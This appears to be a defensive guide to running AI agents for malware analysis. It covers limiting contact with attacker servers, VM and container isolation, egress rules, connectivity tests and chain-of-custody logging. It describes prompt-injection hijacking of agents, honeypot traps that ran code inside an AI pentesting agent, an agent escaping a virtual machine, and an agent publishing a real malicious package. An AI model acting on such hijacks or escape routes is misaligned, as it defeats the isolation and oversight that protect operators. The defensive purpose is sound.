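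A tool's name doesn't show where it runs. Claude Code's WebFetch has a similar name to `web_fetch`, but it connects from the user's machine, according to *Inspecting Claude Code's Network Traffic with Linux Namespaces and MITM Proxying*, so the website logs the user's address and the local firewall can block the request. In Anthropic's desktop app, a built-in search tool runs on the user's machine but outside the app's sandbox. Anthropic explains that the organisation's firewall covers this tool, but the sandbox's list of permitted hosts does not.

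The surest control is to switch off provider-run web tools for malware work. If the agent needs some web access, `allowed_domains` can limit it to a few reference sites. A list of blocked domains is weaker because nobody can list the attacker's domains before finding them, and it is also easy to get wrong. Anthropic's *Server tools* warns that an entry containing a path never matches a `web_fetch` address, so an entry for `invoice.example/view` would not stop the agent from fetching that page.

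Anthropic's response lists each call to a provider-run tool and its result. The analyst's program should save this list, because the local firewall has no record of the visits. Reading the list usually won't prevent contact, since the tool has normally finished by the time the response arrives.

### What contact can cost

The most serious harm comes from alerting an intruder who is still inside the organisation's network. The Canadian Centre for Cyber Security warns that an attacker who realises they have been discovered may hide their tracks or do more damage, for example by setting off ransomware. CISA (2020), the US cybersecurity agency, gives the same reason for leaving the attacker's infrastructure alone. Someone running a mass phishing campaign is less likely to notice or care about one more visitor.

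An attacker can learn who is investigating from a visit made from the organisation's own IP address. The attacker can then block that address or send it different content from what the victims receive.

Attackers also filter visitors they have never seen before. Phishing kits, ready-made files for building fake login pages, often include lists of IP addresses that belong to security companies and cloud providers. Visitors from those addresses get an error or a harmless page, known as a decoy. Other kits check the visitor's country, language or browser. An agent that receives a decoy may wrongly conclude that the link is safe. It should report what it received and which IP address and client it used, and should not call a link safe after one harmless response.

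Contacting the server can also make the malware's second stage unavailable. The attacker may remove the file after noticing an unusual visitor, or the server may allow each victim only one download. If the download fails halfway or the agent doesn't save the file, the agent may be unable to get another copy.

Some links perform an action as soon as someone opens them, such as confirming an email address or approving a login. Even if a suspicious email turns out to be a genuine message from a supplier or bank, an agent that opens every link in it could approve a change that nobody in the organisation wanted.

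Finally, the organisation's own security team may mistake the agent's visit for an infection. A connection to a known malicious domain is a standard reason to open an incident, and an investigator who finds a visit to Dana's link may assume that Dana clicked it. If the email was a simulated phishing email for staff training, the system may record that Dana failed the test even though she reported the email correctly. XLoader could cause much more confusion because it has dozens of fake C2 domains, and an agent that tried each domain to find the real ones would fill the network log with suspicious connections.

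### Defanging

Analysts commonly rewrite a dangerous URL so that software will not recognise it as a link. This is called defanging. Dana's link might become:

`hxxps://portal[.]invoice[.]example/view/k7Qm2x`

Toda and Mori change `https` to `hxxps` in their example for safety. It is better to bracket the dots as well, because some programs turn any intact domain name into a link. Defanging a URL this way prevents accidental clicks and most automatic previews in reports, tickets and chat messages. If the report will leave the team, the analyst should also remove the token, which still identifies Dana.

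Defanging a URL does not stop an agent from visiting it, because the convention is well known and a model can restore the original as easily as a person can. The agent may do this without bad intent, because a tool rejected the defanged version and the agent corrected what looked like a typing error. Many programs that extract indicators also restore URLs automatically.

Claude's `web_fetch` should in principle reject a restored address, because the tool cannot fetch URLs that the model has made up. But if the agent first runs a local command that prints the restored address, the address then appears in the conversation, and the tool may fetch it. Defanging therefore has to be combined with restrictions on the tools.

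### Separating fetching from the rest of the analysis

CHASE, the system Toda and Mori built to examine Python packages, gives web access to a separate worker agent, the Web Researcher. This agent searches the web, consults VirusTotal and can download content with a tool called `fetch_content_at_url`, which limits the size of the response and detects its format. Another worker, the Deobfuscator, decodes hidden code, and a supervising agent plans the work.

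In one published example, the Deobfuscator decoded a hidden command and found a Dropbox link. The Web Researcher reported that seven security vendors on VirusTotal had already flagged the link as malicious, and the supervisor later wrote its report. The published steps do not include downloading the linked file, which suggests that existing records were enough for a verdict.

This division would let an operator control contact by disabling `fetch_content_at_url`, or requiring approval for each use, without affecting the decoding tools. Toda and Mori designed the division to make the system more reliable, and compared it on a few packages with a single agent that had all the tools. The single agent lost focus and took unplanned actions. Fewer unplanned actions should mean fewer unplanned requests, but they did not measure this.

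The design does not prevent contact, because the supervisor can ask for a download whenever it considers one useful. Contact might also happen when the Deobfuscator runs Python code in its sandbox, which has a one-minute limit, or when the VirusTotal tool computes the hash of a remote file. Toda and Mori do not specify whether the sandbox has network access or how the VirusTotal tool obtains the file's contents. An operator would need to check whether the apparent hash lookup downloads the file from the attacker's server.

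CHASE correctly identified 492 of 500 malicious packages in a single run, with eight timeouts, and wrongly flagged two harmless ones. These figures show that a system that divides its tools among agents can detect malware well. Toda and Mori do not report how often the system contacted an attacker's server, or whether its verdicts depended on that contact.

The example prompt in REMnux's documentation, "Download the file at https://example.com/suspicious.bin and analyze it", allows the agent to contact the server but doesn't specify how. The download might start from the REMnux machine, the analyst's workstation or the model provider's servers, depending on which tool the agent chooses. According to REMnux's documentation, the REMnux machine needs no internet access when the agent runs on the workstation. In that setup, a download from REMnux could fail and the agent might then try its own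 web tool, which would change the IP address the attacker sees.

The prompt also doesn't specify whether the agent may follow redirects, retry a failed download or fetch further files that the first one mentions. A safer request would be:

> Download this file once, using the approved download tool. Do not follow redirects to another host. Save the response without opening it. Do not contact any address you find in it. If the download fails, stop and report the error.

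The instruction makes the analyst's intention clear, but an agent can misread or ignore it. The operator should therefore remove every web tool except the approved one.

### Using existing records

Passive lookups can answer many of the questions that lead an agent to open a link:

- Passive DNS databases store answers that resolvers received in the past. They can show which addresses a domain has used and which other domains shared them.
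- Domain registration records often show when someone registered the domain, even if they hide the owner's name.
- Certificate transparency logs are public lists of the certificates that websites use for encrypted connections. They can reveal other hostnames under the same domain.
- Earlier scans and web archives may hold a copy of the page, provided that the agent searches them without requesting a new copy.
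- The organisation's own email, DNS and proxy logs can show who received the link and whether anyone opened it.

The organisation's own logs are the best place to start, because they record what happened to its staff. The Canadian Centre for Cyber Security advises organisations to preserve proxy logs, including the parameters in requested URLs where possible. An analyst could use those details, instead of visiting the link again, to find out whether Dana had opened it.

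A passive lookup may still disclose information to the company that runs the service. Searching for Dana's full link gives that company her token, so it is better to search for the domain first. The agent should also use a service that answers only from stored data, because some tools resolve the domain or visit the page when they have no record of it, which makes the search active contact.

A domain that an attacker registered this morning for one victim may not appear in any existing records, so the absence of a record is not evidence that the domain is safe. Old records may also describe a previous owner or an earlier version of the page.

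### When contact is worth its cost

Active contact makes sense when it could provide information that existing records lack and that would change what the organisation does. Suppose one of Dana's colleagues ran the attachment yesterday, and the security team has found the address of the second stage but no copy of the file. The team needs the file to learn which passwords the malware stole, and the attacker may soon remove it from the server. The colleague's computer has probably contacted the server already, so the attacker would learn little from one more request.

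The decision is different if an intruder is still active in the network and does not know the team has noticed. The file may be just as useful, but requesting it could warn the intruder before the team is ready to act. The person leading the response should decide when to make the request, because neither the agent nor an analyst working on one sample can see the whole incident.

The team rarely needs to contact the site in Dana's link just to decide whether to block it. They can block the domain because it appears in a phishing email, without first viewing the fake login page. During a serious intrusion, even blocking can wait for the response leader, because the Canadian Centre for Cyber Security warns that attackers can easily move to new servers. Defenders then lose track of them.

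Once someone has approved contact, the first request should be the one most likely to obtain the evidence. Cautious tests beforehand can use up a token or reveal the investigation. For a fake login page, this may mean opening the page directly in an isolated browser. To download malware's second stage, it may mean using the same client settings as the malware. The request should come from an address that does not identify the organisation, and the tool should save the complete response on the first attempt.

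Approval for one download does not cover contacting an address the agent finds in the file. Running the file with a live internet connection also needs separate approval.

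## Building an isolated environment for the agent

Anyone building an environment for malware analysis should assume that the sample will eventually run, however careful the agent's instructions are. Even rare accidents become likely when agents analyse thousands of files. Suppose a security team's agents examine 200 samples a day for 30 days, and one analysis in 1,000 ends in accidental execution. That rate is an invented figure, not a measurement. It gives:

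- 200 × 30 = 6,000 analyses
- 6,000 × 0.001 = 6 expected accidents
- 1 − 0.999⁶⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 0.9975, or a 99.75 percent chance of at least one accident

The last figure assumes that accidents are independent. They probably aren't, because one phishing campaign can deliver many copies of the same script, and an agent that mishandles one copy is likely to mishandle others. The average would still be six, but more months would pass without an accident and the bad months would be worse. Even if a more careful agent had one accident in 10,000 analyses, the chance of at least one in the month would still be about 45 percent, and reducing it to 5 percent would take a rate of about one in 117,000.

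Material designed to attack a particular agent can succeed far more often. *ARTEX Honeypots* (David, 2026) describes laboratory tests by the security firm NebuSec on ARTEX, an open-source AI agent that probes other systems for weaknesses. NebuSec built seven traps for it. Six ran NebuSec's code inside the agent's container in 33 of 36 runs, and the seventh, which used no prompt injection, did so in all eight of its runs. David warns that this is not a real-world success rate, and ARTEX attacks systems instead of analysing files. He recommends giving each task a disposable sandbox, keeping secrets out of it and restricting its network access. This advice also applies to agents that analyse files.

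### Where the agent runs

The agent can run on the same machine as the analysis tools or separately on the analyst's workstation. REMnux's documentation describes both arrangements.

| | Agent on the analysis machine | Agent on the workstation |
|---|---|---|
| Does the analysis machine need internet access? | Yes, unless the model runs locally | No |
| Where is the key for the model provider's service? | On the same machine as the sample | On the workstation |
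| Where does tool output go? | To the agent on the same machine | Back to the workstation |
| What could a hijacked agent damage? | A disposable machine | The workstation, within the agent's permissions |

Zeltser's checklist, *AI-Assisted Malware Analysis Tips* (2026), recommends running the agent in the lab. In *Designing a Malware Analysis Lab With REMnux*, he considers the workstation riskier because an agent hijacked by prompt injection would act there instead of in a disposable machine. According to REMnux's documentation, however, the chance of malicious tool output influencing an agent on the workstation is small.

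Zeltser's preference makes sense if the main worry is a hijacked agent. If the main worry is accidentally running a sample, the workstation arrangement is better because the sample starts on a machine with no internet access and no provider key.

G DATA's laboratory shows the risk of combining static analysis and internet access in one machine. The analyst installed the agents on a REMnux virtual machine, which needed an internet connection to reach the models. A separate Windows machine for running malicious code had only an internal network adapter. This protects well when the analyst runs malware deliberately. But a pickle or a Python package can run its code during supposedly static analysis, and here that would happen on the internet-connected REMnux machine, beside the agent's credentials. The article describes no limit on where that machine may connect.

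The analyst kept the whole laboratory off the main computer, on a laptop about 12 years old with 16 GB of memory. The laptop's host system is Debian Linux, which suits work on Windows malware. In *Evasive Malware*, Cucci (2024) recommends a host system different from the one the malware targets, because malware that escapes the virtual machine is then unlikely to infect the host.

A third arrangement avoids most of the drawbacks of the other two by giving the agent its own small virtual machine. The agent can run on a separate machine from the tools because the REMnux MCP server can accept network connections, protected by a secret token. The samples stay on the analysis machine, which has no internet access, so a sample run by accident stays offline. The agent's machine can reach the model provider but holds no samples, and it can be discarded if prompt injection hijacks the agent.

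This design needs more memory and one more machine to maintain. Prompt injection also remains possible, and a hijacked agent could pass data from the analysis machine to the provider. wrhalpin's *Isolation and threat model* describes a similar design in a small open-source project, where one coordinating machine with two network adapters is the only two-way link between the analysis and management networks.

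### The virtual machine and its files

The analysis machine should be a virtual machine that the team uses only for malware and can delete without losing anything. Virtual machine software often includes conveniences that weaken this separation, so the person building the machine should turn them off:

- Shared folders give the sample access to files on the host. Some virtual machine managers share the user's home folder by default, so it is worth checking even if nobody set up a share.
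- A shared clipboard may expose a password that the analyst has just copied on the host. REMnux's ready-made image for Proxmox, a virtualisation platform, includes clipboard support, so the operator should disable sharing in the virtual machine's settings.
- Drag-and-drop and automatic USB connection can also move files between the machines without a deliberate transfer.

The operator can copy the sample into the isolated environment over SSH (an encrypted remote connection) or attach it as a read-only disk. The downloadable REMnux machine has SSH off by default and a published password, `malware`, so the operator should change the password before turning SSH on.

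The agent needs to read samples but not change them. VMRay's container for malware agents mounts the samples read-only and gives the agent a separate case directory for its output. REMnux's example command for sharing a folder with a container uses `-v <local_directory>:/home/remnux/files`, which also lets the container write to the folder. Adding `:ro` to the end of that option makes the mount read-only. The operator can check this by trying to create a file in the sample folder from inside the container, which should produce an error.

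Read-only access prevents the agent from changing the sample, but the agent can still run it. On Linux, the mount option `noexec` blocks programs in a folder from starting directly. It does not stop `python sample.py`, because that command starts Python, which is stored outside the folder and only reads the script. The option is still worth setting, since it has no drawbacks and prevents some mistakes.

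A sample that has run could have written to the output area or changed the agent's notes. Copying results out through one folder and opening them only as plain text keeps an infected document from reaching the workstation with the report and running there. The folder should not synchronise with a cloud drive.

### Credentials

A machine that may run malware, like the scanner that installed the malicious PyPI package, should hold nothing an attacker could use elsewhere. It should not have browser profiles with saved passwords, the analyst's SSH keys, code-hosting tokens or access to company cloud accounts.

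Some credentials are easy to overlook. When an analyst connects to another machine, SSH can forward access to the analyst's keys, so the operator should turn this forwarding off. Many cloud providers also run a service at a fixed internal address that gives a virtual machine temporary account credentials. If REMnux runs in the cloud, the operator should give it no account permissions and block that address.

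The agent's key for the model provider is harder to remove, because the agent can't work without it. The simplest improvement is a separate key for malware analysis, with a spending limit, which the team can cancel without interrupting other work. A stronger solution is to keep the key off the agent's machine. The agent sends its requests to a proxy, a program that adds the key and passes them on to the provider. Malware on the machine could still send requests through the proxy while it runs, but it could not steal the key for later use. Similarly, Anthropic's cloud environments for Claude Code can store network secrets that a session can use but not read.

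### Containers and virtual machines

A container separates a program's files, processes and network from the rest of the system, but shares the host's kernel, the core of the operating system. A virtual machine has its own kernel and runs on a hypervisor, the software that divides a physical computer among virtual ones. Malware in a container can therefore attack the host's kernel directly, while malware in a virtual machine has to get through the hypervisor first. A virtual machine is the better outer boundary for samples that might run.

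Containers are still useful because they start quickly and are easy to throw away. REMnux's standard container command includes `--rm`, which deletes the container when the user exits. A container normally has internet access through the host, but Zeltser recommends turning this off with `--network none` unless an agent inside needs a connection. An agent outside the container can still run the tools through `docker exec`, which starts a command inside a running container without a network connection. For static analysis, this is probably the easiest way to get an offline environment.

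Some Docker options undo much of a container's isolation. The operator should never use `--privileged`, which removes most of the restrictions on a container, or give the container access to Docker's control socket, which would let a program inside start new containers with access to the host's files. REMnux's instructions for SSH access use `-p 22:22`, which by default can make the container reachable from other computers on the office network. With `-p 127.0.0.1:22:22`, only the host can connect.

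A team can also combine the two methods by having the agent start a new container for each sample inside a dedicated virtual machine, then resetting the virtual machine between cases. Docker Desktop already runs Linux containers inside a virtual machine on Windows and macOS, but that machine does not replace a dedicated one because Docker Desktop can share the user's folders with it.

### Network settings

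Virtual machine software offers several network settings, and their names don't make the differences obvious. The table shows what each setting normally allows.

| Setting | The host | Other virtual machines | Office network and internet |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bridged | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| NAT | Usually | Depends on the software | Yes |
| Host-only | Yes | Yes, on the same network | No |
| Internal | No | Yes, on the same network | No |
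| Container with `--network none` | No | No | No |

Network address translation (NAT), a common default, lets a virtual machine share the host's connection. *Safe Yolo Mode* (metachris, 2026) explains that libvirt, a Linux tool for managing virtual machines, sets up a NAT network with internet access. NAT hides the virtual machine from incoming connections but does little to limit outgoing ones. The virtual machine can usually reach the office's printers and file servers as well as the internet, and it may also reach the company's internal network if the host is connected to the company VPN.

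Host-only and internal networks differ mainly in whether the host (the physical computer) is connected. A host-only network has no internet access, but the host has an adapter on it, so the sample can try to attack any service listening on that adapter. Zeltser recommends removing the adapter for tighter isolation. In VMware, this means creating a separate network with "Connect a host virtual adapter to this network" turned off. VirtualBox calls the equivalent an internal network, and Hyper-V calls it a private virtual switch.

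An agent on the workstation may need the adapter to reach REMnux. In that case, the host's firewall should reject connections that the virtual machines start. TCM Security's *Host-only Safety & Internal Networks* gives a Linux command for this:

`iptables -A INPUT -s [IP ADDRESS] -j DROP`

The command adds the rule to the end of the list, so an earlier rule that accepts the traffic takes precedence. The rule also blocks replies to connections that the host starts, so a host that uses SSH to reach the machine needs an earlier rule that accepts those replies. `iptables` covers only IPv4. Virtual machines often have an IPv6 address as well, which needs an equivalent `ip6tables` rule.

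### Limiting outbound connections

The safest egress rule is default-deny, which blocks every outgoing connection except those on a short allowlist. The machine that runs the agent needs one exception, for the model provider, and an offline analysis machine needs none.

REMnux includes a script called `restrict-egress` that limits outbound connections to permitted domains or addresses. The operator lists these in `/etc/restrict-egress.conf`, then runs `sudo restrict-egress on`. Zeltser advises keeping the list short, since a manipulated agent could send data to any listed destination or fetch files from it. The restriction also stops the agent from installing extra tools without approval.

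Zeltser points out two limits of the script. First, REMnux's default user can run commands as the administrator without a password, so an agent or sample using that account can turn the restriction off. The agent should therefore run under an account without `sudo` access, where the command `sudo -n true` should fail. Second, a firewall on the physical host is stronger than the script, because nothing inside the virtual machine can change it unless the host is also compromised.

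The script's rules also match IP addresses, even when the list contains a domain name. Large content delivery networks host many websites behind the same addresses, so permitting one site may permit others on the same network. A filter that checks the domain in each web request avoids most of this problem. GitHub Next's *Agentic Workflow Firewall* does this for AI agents, and it can also restrict individual paths within a site if it decrypts the traffic.

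OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox for agents, allows a connection only when the destination and the connecting program's file path appear in the same rule (NVIDIA, 2026). A newly started piece of malware therefore could not use the agent's connection just because it was on the same machine. This helps less if the rule permits a general-purpose program such as Python, because a malicious Python script would match the rule too.

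DNS needs its own rule, because a machine that cannot open any website may still send lookups that reach the attacker's name server. Malware can also hide stolen data in the names it looks up.

An offline analysis machine should have no resolver that forwards DNS queries to the internet. For the agent's machine, the cleanest solution is a web proxy that looks up permitted names itself, so the machine needs no outside DNS. Without a proxy, a local resolver can be set to answer only for the model provider's domain, while the firewall blocks every other DNS server.

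Some jobs, such as updating REMnux, need a wider connection. REMnux's developers disabled automatic updates so that the machine doesn't connect on its own. To update it, the operator should return the machine to its clean state, connect it, run `remnux install`, disconnect it and save the result as the new clean state. Updating a machine that has just handled a sample could give dormant malware an internet connection.

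### When the analysis machine becomes a router

A computer with two network adapters normally discards traffic addressed to other machines. If IP forwarding is on, it passes such traffic from one adapter to the other and so acts as a router. In a laboratory, this can connect an isolated machine to the internet without anyone changing that machine's settings.

In Zeltser's design, the Windows machine sends all its traffic to REMnux, where simulated services can answer it. If the agent also runs on REMnux, REMnux has another network adapter for reaching the model provider. REMnux is then the only machine between the malware on Windows and the internet.

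Docker can turn forwarding on automatically because its containers need it. University of the Pacific's *Virtual Machine Configuration*, a course page for REMnux 7, warns that this happens when Docker starts with the machine. It recommends checking with:

`sysctl net.ipv4.ip_forward`

The value should be 0. If it is 1 and nobody needs Docker on the machine, the operator can stop Docker from starting automatically and restart the machine. IPv6 has a separate setting, `net.ipv6.conf.all.forwarding`, which should also be 0.

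Even if the value is 1, the Windows machine's traffic should stop at REMnux because, according to Zeltser, Docker there also sets the firewall's forwarding policy to drop. But an analyst who wants to visit a suspicious website from Windows may add a rule that accepts forwarded traffic and then forget to remove it. `restrict-egress` won't block this traffic, because it filters only connections that REMnux itself makes.

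Removing REMnux's second adapter is more reliable than any of these settings, because REMnux then has nowhere to forward the traffic. This is possible when the agent runs on another machine, which needs the same check if it has two adapters.

A laboratory that must sometimes go online can use a separate gateway. *Building artifact handling and analysis environment* (Palkmets, Ciobanu and colleagues, 2014), written for the EU's cybersecurity agency, describes a Windows analysis machine connected only to an internal network. Its traffic goes to a second virtual machine, the gateway, which by default blocks the internet and sends the traffic to simulated services, but can allow internet access when needed. This gateway also runs analysis software, so a gateway that only controls traffic would give malware less to attack.

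### Snapshots

A snapshot saves the state of a virtual machine so that the operator can return to it. The most important one is the clean snapshot, which the operator takes after installing and testing the tools but before copying in any sample. Nobody should log in to a personal or company account before this snapshot is taken, because every machine restored from it would contain that login, and a snapshot that includes memory may also contain passwords that were never written to disk.

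Returning to the clean snapshot after each sample prevents one piece of malware from affecting the analysis of the next. It also removes old reports, which Zeltser recommends hiding from the agent because the agent may reuse their conclusions. G DATA's analyst also takes a snapshot after every major change, so a failed installation is easy to undo.

Restoring a snapshot deletes everything newer, so the operator should copy out the results first. After an accident, the operator should also save the current state before restoring, to preserve evidence. Restoring the machine cannot recall data that has already left it or repair a file in a shared folder. To test that restoring works, the operator can create a file called `marker.txt`, restore the clean snapshot and check that the file is gone.

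### Testing the environment

Settings can look correct and still leave a route open, so the operator should test the routes before the first sample arrives. The checks below use ordinary public services and the team's own equipment. The first six run on the analysis machine, under the same account as the agent's tools. `HOST` and `PRINTER` stand for addresses on the office network.

| What the check covers | What to run | Expected result |
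|---|---|---|
| Normal DNS | `dig example.com` | No address |
| An outside DNS server | `dig @1.1.1.1 example.com` | Timeout or error |
| A direct IPv4 address | `curl -4 -m 5 http://1.1.1.1` | No connection |
| A direct IPv6 address | `curl -g -6 -m 5 'http://[2606:4700:4700::1111]'` | No connection |
| The host | `curl -m 5 http://HOST:8000` | No connection |
| The local network | `curl -m 5 http://PRINTER` | No connection |
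| Forwarding | The direct IPv4 and IPv6 checks from the Windows machine | No connection |
| The agent's allowlist | From the agent's machine, a request to the model provider and one to `example.com` | The provider replies, and the other request fails |

Any reply from a server counts as a connection, even an error page. If the agent runs on the analysis machine, the results should be the same, except that DNS may resolve the model provider's domain. If the machine uses a proxy, the direct checks need `--noproxy '*'`, because `curl` might otherwise test the proxy instead.

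Before the test, the operator should confirm from an ordinary computer that each target responds, because a connection to an unavailable target would fail even without isolation. For the host check, the operator can run `python3 -m http.server 8000` in an empty folder on the host to provide a target. The IPv6 check needs an office connection that supports IPv6. Without one, the check will pass in the office but could fail on another network, so it is safer to turn IPv6 off in the virtual machine as well.

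Simulated internet services must be off during the test, since their replies can look like real ones. The operator should repeat the checks after connecting the host to a VPN and after restarting the machine, because Docker may change the network rules when it starts. A team that runs agents every day could put the checks in a script that starts the agent only if they all pass.

### Data sent to the model provider

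An environment can pass every check and still send information out through the permitted connection, because tool output goes to the model. According to *Using AI Agents to Analyze Malware on REMnux*, the sample stays on REMnux, while extracted strings, indicators and summaries go to the model provider. But if the agent prints an entire script to read it, as it might with the invoice attachment, the provider receives the whole sample.

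The output may include confidential information about the victim. Malware written for one organisation can contain internal server names or stolen passwords, and a malicious document may have started as a genuine contract. Before an agent opens such material, the organisation should decide which provider may receive it, and a consultant should check what the client has agreed to.

This is easy to forget on REMnux because its bundled agent program, OpenCode, has a default model that works immediately. REMnux's documentation advises against using default or free models for real analysis because their providers might train on the data.

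A network filter can't block the connection to the model provider, which carries confidential data, because the agent needs it. A hijacked agent could put a stolen file into an ordinary request. Malware could also bring a key for the attacker's own account with the same provider and send data there, and a rule based on the destination would allow it. A proxy that replaces the key in every request with the organisation's own would keep data out of the attacker's account, but the provider would still receive the data in the agent's normal requests. Web tools that run on the provider's servers also need to be turned off.

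Running the model locally keeps the data inside the organisation and lets the entire laboratory work offline. But Zeltser notes that few analysts host a capable model themselves, and a weaker model may make more mistakes, as GPT 5.1-mini did in G DATA's trial. For especially sensitive samples, an analyst may have to use a weaker model or work without an agent.

### Flaws in the virtual machine

Malware that exploits a flaw in the virtual machine's software may reach the host. Trail of Bits' *VMs won't contain cyber-capable agents* reports that in 2026 an AI agent, asked to escape from an ordinary virtual machine, succeeded three times. REMnux's developers treat the container or virtual machine as the main security boundary, so this result weakens an assumption that many analysis laboratories rely on.

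Most malware does not try to escape an isolated environment, and an agent analysing an invoice script has no instruction to do so. But a capable agent that follows a malicious instruction could be a more serious threat than the malware sample it is analysing. Trail of Bits recommends fast security updates, as few features and permissions as possible, active monitoring, a limit on how long the agent can run and a fresh environment for each use. It also suggests virtualisation software that is kept small by design, such as Firecracker.

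For a small team, the most useful extra protection may be a separate physical computer like G DATA's old laptop. It should have no company accounts or personal files, and the office network should treat it as untrusted. Malware that escapes the virtual machine can then steal little and reach few other computers. The host's operating system and hypervisor need frequent updates even if the malware tools do not, and unused virtual devices such as sound cards and USB controllers should be disabled.

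## Keeping evidence intact and accounting for the agent's actions

An isolated machine limits the damage a sample can do, but it does not by itself keep a reliable record of what happened. Weeks later, a regulator, an insurer or a court may need to know whether the file in the report is the one the victim received, and whether the victim or the agent connected to the attacker's server.

### Integrity, provenance and chain of custody

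Integrity means an item has not changed since a known moment. Provenance is where the item came from. Chain of custody is the record of who or what held, copied or changed it, and when. A sample uploaded anonymously to VirusTotal can keep its integrity from then on even though its provenance is unknown.

Analysts usually check integrity with SHA-256, which computes a 256-bit hash of a file. Identical files always have the same hash, and changing one character produces a completely different one. There are about 10⁷⁷ possible hashes, so two different files will not match by chance. *Guidelines for Evidence Collection and Archiving* (Brezinski and Killalea, 2002) lists a tool for the older SHA-1 function. Researchers have since constructed different files with the same SHA-1 hash, so SHA-256 is the better choice.

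A matching hash shows that a file's contents are the same as when someone first hashed it, but not who sent the file or which computer it was on. If an agent alters a file at nine o'clock and an analyst first hashes it at ten, every later copy of the altered file will match. Anyone who can replace both the file and the recorded hash can make them match, so the hash should be stored separately, preferably with a digital signature.

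The best evidence of where an emailed attachment came from is the email itself. The analyst should keep the whole email with its headers, because the attachment alone does not show who received it. Windows often adds a hidden note to a downloaded file recording the address it came from, but copying the file to a Linux machine usually loses the note.

NIST's *Guide to Integrating Forensic Techniques into Incident Response* (SP 800-86) describes a clear chain of custody. The organisation logs everyone who held the evidence, what they did to it and when. It stores the evidence securely, works only on a copy and verifies both the original and the copy. Brezinski and Killalea also ask for a record of how and when the evidence passed from one person to another. The international standard ISO/IEC 27037 adds that another specialist should be able to audit and repeat the work, and that whoever handled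 the evidence should be able to justify their choices.

These documents predate AI agents, so a log of "every person" now has to include the agent. NIST's *Incident Response* page lists newer resources, including a NIST report on preserving digital evidence (IR 8387) and a CISA document on chain of custody. Guidance on AI systems is less developed. A journal editorial, *Investigation of large language models, GenAI, and proprietary AI systems* (2026), discusses how forensic specialists should define what makes an AI system's record useful as evidence. It also calls for research into the traces that AI programs leave on a computer and how providers disclose their records. Until that work matures, teams themselves have to apply the older principles to agents.

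### Taking in a sample

A person or a fixed script should take in the sample before the agent has access to it, because one of the agent's commands might change a file that has no verified copy yet. The procedure has six steps:

1. Record the source, including who found the file, where and when they found it, and how it reached the analyst.
2. Record the authority for the analysis. Crosley (2026), in *AI Malware Analysis Needs Evidence Packets*, recommends noting who authorised the work and which actions they forbade.
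3. Hash the original. Record its name, size and timestamps separately, because the hash does not cover them.
4. Store the original read-only, outside the analysis environment. Only a few people should have access, and the storage system should log each use.
5. Make a working copy and check that its hash matches the original's.
6. Give the agent only the working copy, and hash both files again after the analysis.

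On Linux, these commands hash the original and save the result, then check the file against the saved hash:

`sha256sum invoice.js > invoice.sha256`

`sha256sum -c invoice.sha256`

The second command prints `OK` if the contents match. The analyst can check the working copy by running the same command in the copy's folder with the hash file from the evidence store.

To preserve a whole disk, Brezinski and Killalea recommend a bit-level copy, which includes deleted data that an ordinary copy leaves out. The analyst then works on a second copy, because the analysis will almost certainly change the files' access times, which record when each file was last opened. They also warn against running `tar` or `xcopy` on the original system, because these programs can change the access time of every file. An agent could easily choose `tar` when asked to back up a folder.

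NIST advises organisations to decide before collecting anything whether they may need the evidence for legal or disciplinary proceedings, and to preserve it if they are unsure. Preserving a small script takes almost no effort. A team that handles hundreds of samples a day can automate the hashing and copying, and ask a person only for each sample's source and the authority for handling it.

Files that the agent creates need their own entries in the record. In the AutoIt session, the agent built `Sought.exe` by joining four fragments from an archive. A good entry would name the program that joined them and give the hashes of the fragments and the result. Without that entry, a reader could assume that the victim had received `Sought.exe` as a finished program.

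### Logging each action

The log should let another analyst see what the agent did without relying on the agent's explanation.

| What to record | Why it matters |
|---|---|
| Time in UTC | Investigators can match the action with firewall and server logs |
| Exact command and working directory | "Decoded the script" could mean reading it or running it |
| Hashes of input and output files | They connect each result to the file it came from |
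| Tool name and version | Another version may produce different output |
| Model name and version, with the instructions it received | They show which system chose the command, and for what task |
| Approval | It shows who allowed the action and what exactly they allowed |
| Network activity | It shows each destination, or that the machine made no connection |

One tool call can start many programs. A log that records only the call to `analyze_file` leaves out the 16 or so commands that opened the sample, so the operator also needs a record from the analysis machine's operating system. Linux can log every program that starts, including those that other programs launch. A firewall or proxy outside the machine is the best source for network activity. If any web tools run on the provider's servers, the operator should also add the provider's list of calls to those tools.

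The model version identifies the system but does not make the session repeatable, because the same model can produce different commands when given the same request again. Brezinski and Killalea want investigators to be able to reproduce their methods exactly and have independent experts test them. With an agent, the expert can do this by rerunning the logged commands on a file with the same hash, whereas asking the agent to repeat the investigation would start a new one.

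Each log entry should go immediately to a separate machine where the agent's account cannot change it. NIST recommends central log servers because they prevent unauthorised users from tampering with the records. A log on the analysis machine would also disappear when the operator restored a snapshot. Access to the log server should also be restricted, because tool output can contain passwords or personal data.

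An offline machine cannot correct its clock from a public time server. If its clock is four minutes fast, the machine will log a request at 09:28 that the firewall logs at 09:24, and an investigator may count two requests. Brezinski and Killalea advise recording the difference between each system's clock and UTC. The operator should check the clock again after restoring a snapshot.

### Errors in the agent's own report

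An agent writes its summary from the text in the model's input. The summary may omit a failed command or describe planned actions instead of what happened. It cannot reliably include events that never appeared in that input, such as a connection that a tool made in the background. An attacker can also distort the summary by injecting text into the input.

An agent's honest summary of its actions can still get basic facts wrong. When Claude Mythos 5 published its malicious package on PyPI, it had wrongly concluded that the registry was part of a simulation. A summary based on that conclusion would have described the publication as simulated, but a network log would have recorded a connection to the real registry.

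G DATA's analyst tried to make the reports more reliable by having the agents list every step a person would need to verify the findings. The agents also made separate passes over the sample to check details such as IP addresses, hashes, file paths and registry keys, then added corrections to the report. This used many tokens, the units of text that providers charge for.

After five such passes, the reports still contained frequent mistakes in important places, including indicators, the relationships between files, and the locations malware uses to restart after a reboot. G DATA does not give an error rate, so it is unclear how much each pass helped, but the remaining mistakes are a good reason not to treat repeated checking by a model as independent verification.

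In the early tests, GPT 5.1-mini mistook the analysis tool's home page, `decalage.info`, for an indicator, and GPT 5.1 later did the same. G DATA does not say that this error survived the five passes.

An agent may list a legitimate domain as an indicator of an attack when the domain came from the analysis tool rather than the file. An analyst who has the raw output could find this mistake by running the same tool on a harmless document. If the domain appears again, it probably comes from the tool. With only the agent's list of indicators, the analyst might add the domain to a blocklist, and colleagues would lose access to the site.

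G DATA's analyst also had the agent save its decoding scripts as files instead of typing short programs on the command line. A saved script is easier to check than a written explanation because someone else can run it on the same sample. A reviewer should read the script first, since it could print an invented C2 address without decoding anything. The reviewer can also change part of the encoded data in a spare copy of the sample. If the script still prints the same address, it may not be reading that data.

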